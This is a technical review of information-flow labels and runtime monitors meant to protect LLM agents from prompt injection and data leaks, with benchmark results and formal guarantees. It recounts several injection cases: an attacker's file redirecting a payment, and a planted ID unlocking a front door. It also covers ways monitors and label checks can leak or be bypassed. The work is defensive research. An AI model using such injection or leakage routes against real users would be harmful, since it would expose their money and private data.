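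FIDES deliberately exempts yes-or-no answers and other values with few possible contents, such as a category from a fixed list. A policy may accept such a value despite its label, because a choice among n possibilities carries at most log₂ n bits. A yes-or-no answer carries at most one bit, and a choice among eight categories at most three. But the limit applies to each value separately, so ten yes-or-no answers can together distinguish 1,024 possibilities.

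Garby and colleagues object that such exemptions make a system hard to audit, because nobody can tell from a run whether a value that got through was a harmless exception or a leak. In LLMbda, a program can raise a value's trust only with an explicit instruction, which a reviewer can search for.

### The banking tests

To test whether an agent can do useful work under these rules, Garby and colleagues wrote one in LLMbda called RANDORI. A model writes a plan, tries it on an invented bank account where all the data is harmless, and revises it if it fails. The model then writes a final plan for the real account. If the agent instead revised its plan after errors on the real account, the labels on the error messages would spread to the new plan.

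They ran RANDORI on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks with three models, three times each. These are the shares of tasks completed without an attack:

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| RANDORI | 75.0% | 75.0% | 64.6% |
| RANDORI, unable to raise trust | not tested | 62.5% | 54.2% |
| CaMeL, checks off | 66.7% | not tested | 70.8% |
| CaMeL, checks on | 37.5% | not tested | 37.5% |

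RANDORI's results are close to those of CaMeL without checks, but the margins of error are around 20 percentage points because there were only 16 tasks. RANDORI has an advantage in the comparison with CaMeL's checks switched on, because its tools enforce only some of CaMeL's policies and its planner may declare untrusted data trusted.

The benchmark pairs each task with nine attacks, giving 144 pairs and 1,296 runs over three models and three repetitions. RANDORI resisted the attack in all but two runs. In 97 pairs, however, the attack needs a tool call that a plan for the user's task would not contain, so an agent that plans before it reads untrusted data usually resists it without any labels. In the other 47 pairs, the plan contains steps that an attack could exploit, and both failures were in this group.

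The attack counts alone are little help in judging the value of the label checks, because CaMeL without its checks also resisted all but 5 attacks in the 622 runs that Garby and colleagues report as completed. In two of the successful attacks, the user had asked CaMeL to follow the instructions in a file, and the planner wrote a loop with a branch for every available tool. The attacker's file could then choose the tools, even though the planner had never read it. With the checks on, CaMeL resisted every attack, so these tests did not trigger either of the gaps in its label tracking.

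### Why the two failures don't contradict the theorem

Both of RANDORI's failures occurred with GPT-5.2 on the same task. The user asked the agent to read a text file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The bank tool accepts only a trusted recipient, so the planner had included an instruction to treat data from the file as trusted. The agent read the attacker's account number, marked it as trusted and paid the attacker.

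The main theorem doesn't cover this program, because the program deliberately raises a trust label. Garby and colleagues have a second theorem for such programs, but it protects only secrets, so it doesn't rule out paying the wrong person. When they removed the instruction that raises the label, the label check blocked the payment, but it would also have blocked a genuine request from the same file.

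### What the theorem leaves to the developer

The theorem assumes that developers label data correctly where it enters the program. LLMbda treats a value without a label as trusted and public, so the agent may send unlabelled medical records to anyone. Developers must also add a label check at every sensitive sink. The theorem guarantees that a value's label reflects everything that influenced the value, but a tool that doesn't check labels will send the value whatever its label is.

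The tools' behavior must also match their descriptions in the program. In the tests, the bank account is a record inside the LLMbda program, and each tool is a function that reads or changes this record. Garby and colleagues acknowledge this as a limitation. If a real payment service also emailed the recipient a receipt, but its LLMbda description omitted this, the theorem would not cover the email.

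Real tools also act while the program is still running, whereas the theorem compares only final results. Suppose an agent counts upwards from 0000 and posts each number publicly, then attempts a forbidden action if the number equals a secret PIN. The label check stops the agent, and the last number posted is the PIN. Aslan Askarov and colleagues showed in 2008 that termination-insensitive guarantees can allow a program that produces output as it runs to leak more than one bit this way.

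Finally, the theorem doesn't cover information that observers get by other routes. LLMbda doesn't model time, so an observer could still learn something from how long a reply takes. The theorem's observers also don't include the company that hosts the model, which receives every message in the conversation, including the secret ones. The theorem assumes that the probability of a reply doesn't depend on text outside the current conversation, which would be false if the company's service remembered earlier conversations.

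### PACE and its hypotheses

In *PACE*, Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) aim for a more limited guarantee, which they state falls short of noninterference. The PACE monitor checks each tool call just before it runs. It records data flows as arrows in a graph, for example from a file to the tool call that read it. The monitor looks for paths in this graph from protected or untrusted data to an unsafe effect and tries to cut them. It also checks whether the user's request authorised the call's effects, such as sending an email to a particular address.

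PACE can cut only arrows that belong to the pending call, because earlier calls have already happened. It can block the call or remove every argument that such a path goes through. Removing an argument is enough only if the agent would have made the call whatever the argument contained. Developers can rarely establish this for a call that a model chose to make, so PACE usually has to block the call.

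Li and colleagues prove that after the cut, the graph contains no path from the protected or untrusted data to the unsafe effect. To conclude that the real data can't get there either, they need further hypotheses. This table compares their five main ones with the situation in LLMbda:

| Hypothesis for PACE | In LLMbda |
|---|---|
| The graph contains every step of the flow | The language's rules guarantee this inside the program; developers must ensure it for outside tools |
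| Every relevant effect passes through the monitor | Developers must put a check in every sensitive tool |
| Protected data, untrusted data and unsafe effects have the right labels | Developers must label sources and set the limits of sinks correctly |
| Blocking a call or changing an argument really stops the flow | A failed check stops the program |
| Nothing relevant changes between the check and the call | True for data inside the program; developers must ensure it for outside files and services |

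The last hypothesis can fail when two calls overlap. For example, PACE might approve the upload of a harmless shared file, but another call might write a password into the file before the upload starts. The upload would then send the password. Li and colleagues describe a stricter protocol that lets only one call proceed at a time, but they tested a partial version that works only within a single process.

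The first hypothesis is the hardest for an agent to meet, because a language model doesn't preserve the identity of the data it reads. PACE can follow a value that a tool passes on unchanged. If the model rewrites the value, PACE searches for known altered forms, including base64 and hexadecimal encodings. This search is a detector, and it can miss paraphrases, translations and short fragments. For example, it would miss Alice's phone number written out in words. The check on the user's request could still block an email to a stranger, but the guarantee about data flow would not apply. LLMbda avoids this problem by giving every reply the label of the whole conversation, which leads to more over-labelling.

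Li and colleagues also prove a negative result about approving tools in advance. They consider two email skills (reusable packages of code and written instructions for an agent) with the same code, which sends whatever text the model provides. One skill's instructions give a fixed template, while the other's tell the model to include a password. A reviewer who examines only the code must reach the same verdict on both, so they can't safely exempt either from checks at run time.

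The data-flow guarantee also doesn't cover every call in the PACE experiments. The tested version of PACE differs from the certified one in that it can let a blocked call go ahead if the user's request authorised its effects, and can repair a call without checking the result again.

An experiment with Qwen-3.8-27B suggests why they relaxed the rules. On a set of AgentDojo cases, the agent completed 76.8% of tasks without a defence, 64.6% with only the check on the user's request, and 13.6% with only the check on data flow. Each check alone stopped every attack in this set, so the data-flow check reduced task completion far more without stopping any additional attacks.

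## Who sets the labels, and when may they be lowered?

The noninterference theorem for LLMbda assumes that data is already labeled correctly, and it covers only programs that never deliberately lower a label. In a working agent, someone has to decide whether the meeting notes are secret and when a sentence from them may go to a client. Both decisions can depend on what the text contains. A developer who has replaced the detector at the sink with a label check may therefore still need a detector to assign labels or to decide when to lower them.

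### A gate with hand-written labels

Thornton, Pritom and colleagues (2026), in *Privacy Conductor*, tested how much depends on the first of these decisions. They built a gate that controls which of a clinic's documents an assistant may retrieve for the person using it. The gate reads neither the documents nor the wording of the request, so nobody can talk it into a release. It decides from facts about the requester and from the document's label, mainly these two fields:

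- the sensitivity tier, one of seven levels such as "internal", "clinical standard" and "financial";
- the access list, which names the roles that may receive the document, such as doctor or nurse.

To open a document about a person, the requester needs both a role on the access list and an assignment to that person. For example, a nurse can open the charts of patients in her care but not those of other patients.

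The test had 105 documents and 24 people, including patients, doctors, nurses and billing staff. Every person requested every document, making 24 × 105 = 2,520 decisions. With labels the researchers wrote by hand, the gate allowed 259 requests and refused 2,261, exactly as the policy required. Any correctly written program would do the same. The result is mainly useful because it means any later error must come from a label.

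### Replacing the person with a model

Thornton and colleagues then had language models write the labels and left everything else unchanged. Each model received a document's title, type and full text, along with the name of the person it was about. It also received definitions of the tiers and roles, and guidance on which roles normally need which kind of record.

| Model | Tier correct | Access list correct | Wrongly released (of 2,261) | Wrongly refused (of 259) |
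|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.8 | 78% | 55% | 40 | 31 |
| Opus 4.8, no extended thinking | 83% | 57% | 44 | 27 |
| Sonnet 5 | 82% | 52% | 64 | 34 |
| Haiku 4.5 | 84% | 30% | 39 | 28 |
| GPT-5.4 | 86% | 23% | 9 | 100 |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 83% | 80% | 11 | 26 |
| GPT-5.4-nano | 82% | 69% | 16 | 36 |

To find the cause of each error, the researchers restored one field at a time to its hand-written value. They traced every wrongful release to the access list.

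The tier is easy to infer because 19 of the 21 document types always have the same tier, and the models had access to the type. An access list instead records a decision by the clinic. Whether billing staff may open a particular record depends on how the clinic organises its billing, which isn't in the record. Thornton and colleagues conclude that even a more capable model couldn't recover the list. Their table only partly supports this, because GPT-5.4-mini got 80% of the lists right, so the document and the guidance together often determined the answer. One person wrote all the reference labels, and a second person might also have disagreed with some of them.

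GPT-5.4 got the fewest lists right but caused the fewest wrongful releases. It added more roles than it left out, but an extra role releases a document only if somebody in that role is also assigned to the patient. The assignments were still written by hand, which kept many of the model's mistakes from releasing documents. They couldn't make up for missing roles, and GPT-5.4 refused 39% of the legitimate requests.

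### The same documents, labelled five times

A second experiment measured how consistently models label documents, so its results don't depend on whether the hand-written labels were right. Each model labelled the same documents five times from identical instructions, and the researchers counted the decisions that differed between rounds. The count ranged from 13 of 2,520 for GPT-5.4-nano to 124 for Haiku 4.5. If a company has a model label its documents only once, chance determines which of several possible policies it gets.

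For Opus 4.8, the number of wrongful releases varied between 34 and 57. The Anthropic models ran with their default random sampling, while the OpenAI models ran with as little randomness as their settings permitted, so the two companies can't be fairly compared on these figures. A model can also be consistently unsafe. GPT-5.4 made nine wrongful releases in every round, and its 40 decisions that changed between rounds all concerned requests that the policy allows.

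A majority vote over the five rounds barely helped. It left 33 wrongful releases for Opus 4.8. For Sonnet 5 it left 66, more than in any single round. A vote can remove mistakes a model makes occasionally, but it keeps those the model makes in most rounds.

Sonnet 4.6 wrote the synthetic documents from the hand-written labels, so they may contain hints about the right answers that real medical records wouldn't. Such hints would make the models look better than they are, but nobody has yet repeated the test on a real clinic's files.

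The last test used real cases and had no gate. The models judged 214 disclosures from court cases under HIPAA, the US law on the privacy of health records. GPT-5.4-mini did best, agreeing with the court-based answer in 87.8% of cases, but it permitted 11 of the 20 disclosures that the law prohibited. Accuracy is a poor measure here because a model that permitted all 20 and got the other 194 right would have scored 90.7%. Twenty cases are too few to estimate the error rate precisely, but they are enough to show that the detector sometimes misses prohibited disclosures.

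### Why tools may be easier to label

A developer can label tools instead of documents, so that everything a tool returns gets the same label. Ji, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems*, describe a monitor called SEAgent that works this way. A language model proposes the labels, and people then check and correct them. According to the paper, this took little human work and gave accurate labels on InjecAgent, a benchmark with 80 labelled tools. Each tool gets five attributes:

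| Attribute | Possible values |
|---|---|
| What the tool acts on | local, external, physical |
| What it does | read, write, execute |
| Sensitivity of the operation | low, moderate, high |
| Integrity of its output | trusted, unfiltered |
| Privacy of its output | general, personal |

A tool that unlocks the front door, for example, acts on something physical, executes and has high sensitivity.

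Labeling tools may be easier than choosing access lists for documents because a tool's description contains most of the information needed. It usually shows whether the tool only reads data or also changes it, much as a document's type indicates its tier. A company may also have only a few dozen tools but many thousands of documents, so a person can check every tool label. The number of options wouldn't explain a difference, since a tool has 3 × 3 × 3 × 2 × 2 = 108 possible labels and a clinic with six roles has only 2⁶ = 64 possible access lists. Nobody has compared the two tasks directly with the same models and the same measure.

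With these labels and four rules, SEAgent stopped every attack in InjecAgent and AgentDojo. But each tool's label has to cover everything the tool might return. In a test without attacks, SEAgent raised two false alarms, both when the agent looked something up on Wikipedia and then tried to record health data or book an appointment. Ji and colleagues had labelled Wikipedia's output "unfiltered". They suggest labelling it "trusted" in practice, which would have prevented both false alarms. However, anyone can edit Wikipedia, so the change would also let an attacker's text trigger sensitive actions. Someone has to decide which risk to accept, and the tool's description isn't enough to decide it.

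### Data without a label

New tools and old files often have no label. LLMbda and Microsoft's Agent Framework both treat unlabelled data as public, so an unlabelled salary file can leave the company. The most restrictive default, untrusted and secret, would prevent this, but the agent could do hardly anything after one call to an unlabelled tool.

*APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) delays the decision instead. Its monitor marks the data as "unknown", which is not a level between trusted and untrusted. The agent keeps working, and its context keeps its established label along with a list of the unlabelled sources it has absorbed. If the agent only uses the data to answer the user's question, nobody may ever need the label. When a sink requires the label, the monitor looks for a cast, a function that the developers registered in advance to label such data. If no suitable cast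 exists, the monitor blocks the call.

A cast can be a classifier that reads the text. To limit the damage from its mistakes, developers declare a ceiling, the most permissive label that the cast may assign. In the notation used for FIDES, where a ⊑ b means that b is at least as restrictive as a, a cast with ceiling c may return a label λ only if

c ⊑ λ.

The context's label L then becomes L ⊔ λ, so a cast can never lower a restriction that already applies.

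Suppose the ceiling for a document search is "untrusted, readable by all staff". The classifier may return this label or a stricter one, such as "readable by the personnel department", but it can't return "public". If it misses a salary in a document, the agent could send the salary to any colleague but not to an outsider. This limit holds even if an attacker wrote the document to deceive the classifier.

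Mistakes within the ceiling still matter. Kravchenko and colleagues prove that a call which passes the monitor's check would also pass if every source had its correct label. The proof assumes that each cast is sound, meaning it never returns a label more permissive than the correct one. AudAgent's theorem likewise assumes that Presidio makes no dangerous errors. Developers could avoid the soundness assumption by choosing a ceiling strict enough for every document in the source, but then they could give every document the ceiling as its label and wouldn't need a classifier.

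### Who may release what, where and when

Once the meeting notes have made the context secret, it stays secret whatever else the agent reads. Some part of the system must be able to make exceptions, or the agent can never tell the client that the meeting has moved. Deliberately lowering a confidentiality label is called declassification, and raising a trust label is called endorsement.

Andrei Sabelfeld and David Sands surveyed the research on declassification in 2009 and sorted policies by four questions. Here they are for an agent that answers a manager's question about an employee's calendar:

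- Who may release the information? Only the employee's own agent may.
- What may it release? It may say whether a time slot is free, but not what is in the slot.
- Where in the system may the release happen? It may happen only in the scheduling tool's reply.
- When may it happen? It may happen only after the manager has proposed a meeting.

A policy that covers only some of these questions can permit far more than its author intended. If it specifies only the employee's agent, that agent may send the manager the whole calendar.

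APPA has separate mechanisms for who may approve a release and what gets released. An authority, which may be a fixed rule, a person or another language model, can approve one exact call, but the approval doesn't change the context's label or carry over to other calls. A sanitiser produces a cleaned version of a text, for example with personal data removed, and the developers decide in advance which label that version gets. Both can bring a detector back into the trusted base, because a model acting as an authority can approve the wrong email and a redaction tool can overlook a name. The developers also declare in advance how much each authority may approve, which limits such errors but doesn't prevent them.

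SEAgent can also ask the user to approve a suspicious call before it runs. The user can block the call, allow it once or choose "always allow this pattern". The third option adds a permanent rule that takes priority over the other rules, so one hurried click can authorise later calls along the same path of agents and tools.

Exceptions have a large effect on how much an agent gets done. Kravchenko and colleagues tested APPA on 20 office scenarios built around obstacles such as missing approvals. With one model, GPT-5.6 Luna, the agent completed 88% of its runs. Completion fell to 35% when APPA blocked calls without suggesting a remedy, and to 56.5% when the agent couldn't read risky data in a separate branch. No attack succeeded in any of these versions, but attacks succeeded in 30% to 39.5% of runs when the checks were open. The scenarios suit APPA, so its completion rate on ordinary office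 work could differ.

### Keeping the attacker out of the decision

Suppose a policy lets an agent send a client "the document the client asked about". An attacker writes to the agent in the client's name and asks about the salary file. The right agent then releases a document at the right time and place, but the attacker has chosen which document.

Steve Zdancewic and Andrew Myers described this problem for ordinary programs in 2001. They called declassification robust if an attacker who can change untrusted data learns no more than one who only watches. A monitor can enforce this with trust labels by releasing a value only if the value is trusted and only trusted data influenced the decision to release it. To check the second condition, the monitor uses the label pc, which records what led to the current step. In the example, the client's email is untrusted, so the monitor would refuse to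 release a document chosen on the basis of that email. It would also refuse the client's genuine requests unless someone confirmed them.

Endorsement raises the same problem. Ji and colleagues ran CaMeL in a simulated smart home, where the owner asked the agent to let in his daughter and said her ID was in a recent message. An attacker had added a different ID to the message. CaMeL followed its plan, read the message and gave the attacker access to the front door. The owner meant to trust the message only for the ID, but the attacker could supply the ID. A policy requiring a trusted ID would have blocked the attacker, but it would also have kept the daughter out.

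### Endorsement that cannot release secrets

LLMbda makes such decisions visible in the program with an instruction called `endorse`, which takes a target label and a value. In an example by Garby and colleagues, an agent replies to incoming email and uses a category as the subject line. A quarantined model reads each email and suggests the category. This suggestion is untrusted, but the email tool accepts only trusted subject lines, so the program converts the suggestion into one of a few fixed tags and endorses the tag.

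The instruction takes only the trust part from the target label and keeps the value's own confidentiality. The new label is

pc ⊔ (trust of the target, confidentiality of the value).

Suppose the email is also secret and the program names (trusted, public) as the target:

| pc | Label of the tag before | Label of the tag after |
|---|---|---|
| (trusted, public) | (untrusted, secret) | (trusted, secret) |
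| (untrusted, public) | (untrusted, secret) | (untrusted, secret) |

In the first row, the tag becomes trusted but remains secret, although the target label includes "public". If `endorse` copied the whole target label, a program could use it to release secrets. In the second row, a model wrote the code after reading an attacker's email. Such code runs with an untrusted pc, so its `endorse` instruction has no effect.

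Plain noninterference can't hold for trust in a program that uses `endorse`, because `endorse` exists to let untrusted data influence trusted results. Garby and colleagues prove what they call insulated noninterference, which covers every observer who sees data regardless of its trust label. With the four labels above, that observer sees all public data, which is everything up to (untrusted, public). Changing a secret can affect whether the program finishes, but otherwise the probabilities of the results this observer sees stay compatible, in the sense defined for LLMbda. This holds whatever the program endorses and whatever text the attacker supplies.

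The weakening therefore stays within one dimension of the label. Likewise, an instruction that lowered confidentiality would leave the guarantee about trust intact, so declassifying a document couldn't give an attacker influence over a payment. The theorem's protection depends on how the developers divide their labels into the two dimensions. If they put everything into the dimension that `endorse` may change, `endorse` can change any label and the theorem guarantees nothing.

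The theorem also doesn't protect trust from a careless endorsement, such as the one that led RANDORI to pay an attacker. A program can even endorse a whole text and then run it as trusted code, and any `endorse` instructions inside it would take effect. Garby and colleagues sketch one restricted version of `endorse` that prevents this chain and another that accepts only values from a small set. Neither version affects the theorem about secrets, but the researchers have not formally characterised what the restrictions achieve for trust.

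### How much short answers reveal

FIDES can exempt short answers from its policies because a reply with k possible values reveals at most log₂ k bits. The bits add up, however. After m such replies, an observer has seen one of at most kᵐ sequences, which gives a limit of

m × log₂ k bits.

Twenty yes-or-no replies can reveal up to 20 bits. That is enough to identify any six-digit code, since 20 bits distinguish 2²⁰ = 1,048,576 possibilities. The limit is the same when each question depends on the earlier answers. If the observer can also notice when no reply comes, for example because a label check stopped the agent, each question has three possible outcomes, and twenty questions can reveal up to 31.7 bits.

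APPA lets a branch of the agent read risky data and return only a form with fixed fields. In one example, the branch reads a public bug report and returns a ticket number, a severity and the name of a component. If there are four severities and eight components, those two fields carry at most 2 + 3 = 5 bits. A ticket number between 0 and 9,999 adds about 13.3 bits, enough to encode a four-digit PIN. A hijacked branch that has read the PIN could return it as the ticket number, and the form would still be valid. Kravchenko and colleagues therefore don't let the form lower a label by itself. The developers must decide separately that its contents may count as trusted or public.

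The number of bits doesn't measure harm. One bit is enough to reveal whether a patient has HIV. The same applies when untrusted data influences what an agent does. An attacker who can only choose among eight subject lines for a reply controls three bits and does little damage, but choosing between "approve" and "refuse" for a refund takes one bit and decides whether the money is paid.

The limit can also overstate what an attacker learns when he can't choose his questions freely. *Assuming You Knew* (Naumann, 2026) gives a typical policy for a password check, which reveals whether a guess was correct as long as there have been fewer than ten guesses. Ten yes-or-no answers could carry 10 bits, but each wrong guess rules out only one password. Against a random four-digit PIN, ten different guesses have a 10 in 10,000 (0.1%) chance of success. With only 20 possible passwords, they would succeed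 half the time. Naumann points out that even this policy is unacceptable when the set of passwords is too small.

### A flawed proof about release policies

A policy that permits some leaks needs a more complicated definition of security than noninterference. Naumann describes the observer's knowledge as the set of secret inputs that he still considers possible. Let K be this set before the program produces an output and K′ the set afterwards. Let R be the set of inputs that agree with the real one on everything the policy releases. The output is secure if

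K′ ⊇ K ∩ R.

In words, the observer may rule out an input only if the policy allowed him to learn the fact that rules it out. (K already takes into account that the observer knows another output will come, so the definition permits leaks through whether the program continues.)

Suppose a user tries to guess a four-digit PIN and wrongly enters 1234. Before the program responds, all 10,000 PINs are possible, so K contains all of them. The policy allows the program to reveal only that the guess was wrong, so R contains the 9,999 other PINs. If the program prints "wrong", K′ contains the same 9,999 PINs and the output is secure. If it also prints the PIN's first digit, at most 1,000 PINs remain possible, so K′ no longer contains all of K ∩ R and the output is insecure.

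In a 2018 paper, Naumann and a co-author published a theorem connecting a definition of this kind to conditions that a monitor can check as a program runs. According to the theorem, a program that met those conditions would reveal only what its policy released. The published proof had a significant flaw, which they announced when they presented the paper. They also sketched a corrected definition and proof.

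Naumann has completed the correction in Rocq, a proof assistant similar to Lean. He had Claude Code, a programming agent, translate the corrected paper into Rocq definitions and finish the proofs. Rocq confirmed that the announced correction was basically right but exposed errors in its details. The theorem covers small programs that read inputs and print outputs, and a proof for an agent has to handle more. Careful researchers twice made mistakes about even these simple programs, which is a good reason to have a computer check any proof about lowering labels. Rocq can't check whether ten guesses are too many for the passwords people choose.

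## Can a detector's error rate be carried through the proof?

The soundness proofs for AudAgent and APPA assume that their detectors never make a dangerous mistake. A proof could instead use the detector's error rate to bound the probability of a violation. *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents*, by Alaia Solko-Breslin and colleagues at Google DeepMind, Google and two universities, does this for policies written in Datalog, which FORGE also uses.

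### What a threshold discards

A monitor loses information when it applies a threshold to a detector's score. In an example from the paper, a policy forbids sending an outside service anything that depends on a message with proprietary information. The user first types in unreleased revenue figures for "Project Horizon", then asks for a press release based on them. A classifier gives the first message a score of 0.45 and the second 0.25. With a threshold of 0.5, both count as harmless, so the monitor lets the agent send the figures out.

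Suppose the scores are accurate probabilities, so that 45% of all messages with a score of 0.45 really are sensitive. The chance that at least one of the two messages is sensitive then depends on how the two events overlap:

| Relation between the messages | Chance that at least one is sensitive |
|---|---|
| The second is sensitive only if the first is | 0.45 |
| Independent | 1 − 0.55 × 0.75 ≈ 0.59 |
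| Never both sensitive | 0.45 + 0.25 = 0.70 |

A monitor that assumes the worst case calculates a risk of 0.70 and blocks the call if the company accepts a risk of at most 0.5. Lowering the classifier's threshold to 0.25 would also block this call, but it would block every call that depends on a single message with a score of 0.25 too. Solko-Breslin and colleagues therefore keep the probabilities and apply one threshold at the end, to the risk of the whole action.

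### From test results to an upper bound

For tools that don't return a score, the probabilities have to come from tests. Suppose an engineer runs a redaction tool on N documents and it leaves personal data in k of them. The observed rate k/N could be too low by luck. The paper uses the Clopper–Pearson bound, which is the failure rate u at which a result of k or fewer failures would have a probability of only α. In terms of the inverse distribution function F⁻¹ of a beta distribution,

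u = F⁻¹(1 − α; k + 1, N − k).

Without any failures, the formula becomes much simpler. A tool with failure rate u gets through N independent trials with probability (1 − u)ᴺ, and setting this to 5% gives

u = 1 − 0.05^(1/N).

After N = 300 trials without a failure, u is about 1%, so the engineer can claim with 95% confidence that the tool fails at most 1% of the time. With three failures in 300 trials, the bound is about 2.6%, although the observed rate is 1%.

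An agent may call the tool many times in one task. The union bound adds up the failure probabilities, so if each call has a 1% chance of failing, the chance that at least one of 50 calls fails is at most 50 × 1% = 50%. It would be about 39% if the failures were independent, and only 1% if the calls always failed together. Guaranteeing a total of at most 1% with the union bound requires a failure rate of at most 0.02% per call, and showing this takes about 15,000 trials without a failure.

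The chance that a measured bound is wrong also adds up across tools. If an engineer bounds the failure rates of ten tools at 95% confidence each, the chance that at least one bound is wrong can be as high as 50%. Testing each tool at 99.5% confidence reduces that maximum to 5%, but a 1% bound then requires about 530 failure-free trials per tool instead of 300.

The trials must also be independent. *Beyond Aggregate Risk* (Rahman, Rahman and colleagues, 2026) uses the same bound for tool-call arguments and warns that arguments from the same agent run may be correlated, which can make the bound too optimistic.

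### Redact, merge and send

In the paper's main example, an agent prepares a file for an outside supplier with four commands:

1. Redact `a.txt` and save the result as `i1.txt`.
2. Join `b.txt` and `i1.txt` into a new file, `i2.txt`.
3. Copy `i2.txt` to `res.txt`.
4. Email `res.txt` to the supplier.

Before the last command runs, the monitor must calculate the probability that `res.txt` contains sensitive data. It starts from three base facts: `a.txt` is sensitive with probability 0.9, `b.txt` is sensitive with probability 0.2, and the redaction tool fails with probability 0.1.

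Datalog rules describe what each command does to the data. A redacted file is sensitive if the original was sensitive and the redaction failed. A combined file is sensitive if either part is, and a copy is sensitive if the original is. So `res.txt` is sensitive exactly when

(a is sensitive ∧ redaction fails) ∨ b is sensitive.

If the three facts are independent, the part before "∨" has probability 0.9 × 0.1 = 0.09, and the risk is 0.09 + 0.2 − 0.09 × 0.2 = 0.272. But the facts could also be related in this way:

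| a.txt sensitive? | Redaction fails? | b.txt sensitive? | Probability | Leak? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Yes | Yes | No | 0.1 | **Yes** |
| Yes | No | Yes | 0.2 | **Yes** |
| Yes | No | No | 0.6 | No |
| No | No | No | 0.1 | No |

The three base facts have the same probabilities as before, but the risk is now 0.30. That is the maximum, because a leak requires either a failed redaction (0.1) or a sensitive `b.txt` (0.2). If the company blocks anything with a risk of 0.30 or more, a monitor that assumes independence allows this email, while one that assumes the worst case blocks it.

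The gap between the calculated risk and the true risk grows when an agent repeats a step. Suppose it redacts the same file twice with a tool that fails 10% of the time. If the failures are independent, the chance that both passes fail is 0.1 × 0.1 = 1%. But a tool that overlooks a phone number written in words will probably overlook it again, and the risk then stays at 10%. After ten passes, the calculated risk is one in ten billion, but the true risk could still be 10%. Most earlier probabilistic Datalog systems assume independence, which Solko-Breslin and colleagues consider unsafe for checking policies.

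### Searching for the worst case

The monitor can find the worst case by solving an optimisation problem. Let x be one complete assignment of "true" or "false" to all n facts in the trace, including derived facts such as "`i1.txt` is sensitive". Let μ(x) be its unknown probability. The monitor maximises

R = Σ μ(x), summed over every x in which the outgoing file is sensitive,

under these conditions:

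- No μ(x) is negative, and together they add up to 1.
- μ(x) = 0 if x contradicts a rule, for example by calling `res.txt` clean and `i2.txt` sensitive.
- For each base fact, the probabilities of the assignments in which it is true add up to a number between its measured lower and upper bounds.

All these conditions are linear in μ, so this is a linear program that standard software can solve. Its maximum, R*, is the highest risk consistent with all the information available to the monitor. The drawback is that the number of unknowns doubles with each added fact. The example's six facts give 2⁶ = 64 unknowns, but 30 facts would give more than a billion, too many for a monitor to solve for before every tool call.

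### A relaxation that never underestimates

Solko-Breslin and colleagues make the problem smaller by keeping only the probability of each fact and of each pair of facts. For 30 facts, that is 465 unknowns. Pairs are enough to express the rules, because a rule with many conditions can become a chain of steps with two inputs each. In the example,

P(i1) = P(a and fail),
P(i2) = P(i1) + P(b) − P(i1 and b).

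Some tables of such numbers are impossible. For example, three events that each occur half the time can't be mutually exclusive, because their probabilities would add up to 150%. To rule out many impossible tables, the program arranges the numbers in a matrix M and requires vᵀMv ≥ 0 for every vector v. Such a matrix is called positive semidefinite, and the whole problem is a semidefinite program.

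Real probabilities always meet this requirement. If xᵢ is 1 when fact i is true and 0 otherwise, vᵀMv is the average of (v₀ + v₁x₁ + … + vₙxₙ)², and the average of a square can't be negative. For the three impossible events, the average of (1.5 − x₁ − x₂ − x₃)² would be −0.75, so the program rejects their claimed probabilities.

The soundness proof is short. Take any distribution that the linear program allows and calculate the probabilities of its facts and pairs. These numbers satisfy every condition of the semidefinite program and give the same risk. The semidefinite program therefore searches through everything that the linear program does, and possibly more, so its maximum is at least as high:

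R* ≤ R_SDP.

If R_SDP is below the company's limit, R* is too. The reverse doesn't hold, because the semidefinite program also accepts some tables that no distribution could produce. The program may therefore overestimate the risk and block an action that the exact calculation would allow.

The program printed in the paper allows more of these tables than necessary because it doesn't require P(u and w) to lie between 0 and the smaller of P(u) and P(w). In the example, this lets P(a and fail) reach 0.18, although redaction fails only 10% of the time, and the calculated risk is about 0.50 instead of 0.30. Real probabilities satisfy the missing condition, so adding it gives 0.30 without affecting the proof. The good test results suggest that the researchers' software includes this condition or something similar. The proof also applies to the exact maximum, which numerical software only approximates,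 so a strict guarantee needs a small safety margin.

Engineers can add what they know about correlations. For example, two files from the same folder may tend to be sensitive together, which means P(u and w) ≥ P(u)P(w). The product of two unknowns isn't linear, so the program replaces it with a new variable t and adds linear conditions that the true product must satisfy. If ℓᵤ and ℓ_w are the lower bounds on the two probabilities, then (P(u) − ℓᵤ)(P(w) − ℓ_w) ≥ 0, which gives

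t ≥ ℓ_w P(u) + ℓᵤ P(w) − ℓᵤ ℓ_w.

Three similar conditions use the upper bounds.

### Results against three alternatives

The researchers tested the method on 197 sequences of shell commands from the Intercode benchmark and 377 agent runs from ATBench. They compared it with three alternatives. Praline is an earlier system that also computes sound bounds for correlated facts. The Monte Carlo method assumes independence and simulates each run 10,000 times. The third applies a threshold to each score separately, and the researchers report its results for the best of nine thresholds.

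"Security" is recall, the share of actions above the risk limit that a method blocks. "Utility" is precision, the share of blocked actions that really are above the limit. These are the results for a limit of 50%:

| Method | Intercode: security | Intercode: utility | ATBench: security | ATBench: utility | Average time, Intercode / ATBench |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Praline | 100% | 97.9% | 100% | 100% | 1.0 s / 7.2 s |
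| Monte Carlo | 70.2% | 100% | 91.9% | 100% | not reported |
| Separate thresholds | 70.2% | 100% | 95.0% | 100% | not reported |
| Semidefinite program | 100% | 100% | 100% | 100% | 0.2 s / 0.3 s |

Praline lost some precision because it ran out of time on several tasks and used rougher bounds. With a limit of 80%, the semidefinite program was less precise than Praline on ATBench (98.3% against 99.6%). It was also slower on six tasks about leaks in cryptographic software, averaging 1.9 seconds against Praline's 0.3.

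Assuming independence can also make the estimate too high. If ten files are each sensitive with probability 20% and always sensitive together, the chance that at least one is sensitive is 20%, but assuming independence gives 89%. In a test where the researchers declared all the input files positively correlated and set the limit at 20%, Monte Carlo's precision fell to 60.6%, while the semidefinite program reached 98.2%.

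These results don't show how many leaks the method would prevent. For the agent benchmarks, the researchers counted an action as a violation if the exact linear program put its risk above the limit, without checking whether data had leaked. They also drew the detectors' probability bounds and the redaction failure rates at random instead of measuring them. The semidefinite program's perfect security score follows from its soundness proof, so the tests provide new information only about its precision and speed. Monte Carlo's 70.2% means that its risk estimates often fell below the worst case. If real errors were independent, many of its decisions to allow an action would have been right.

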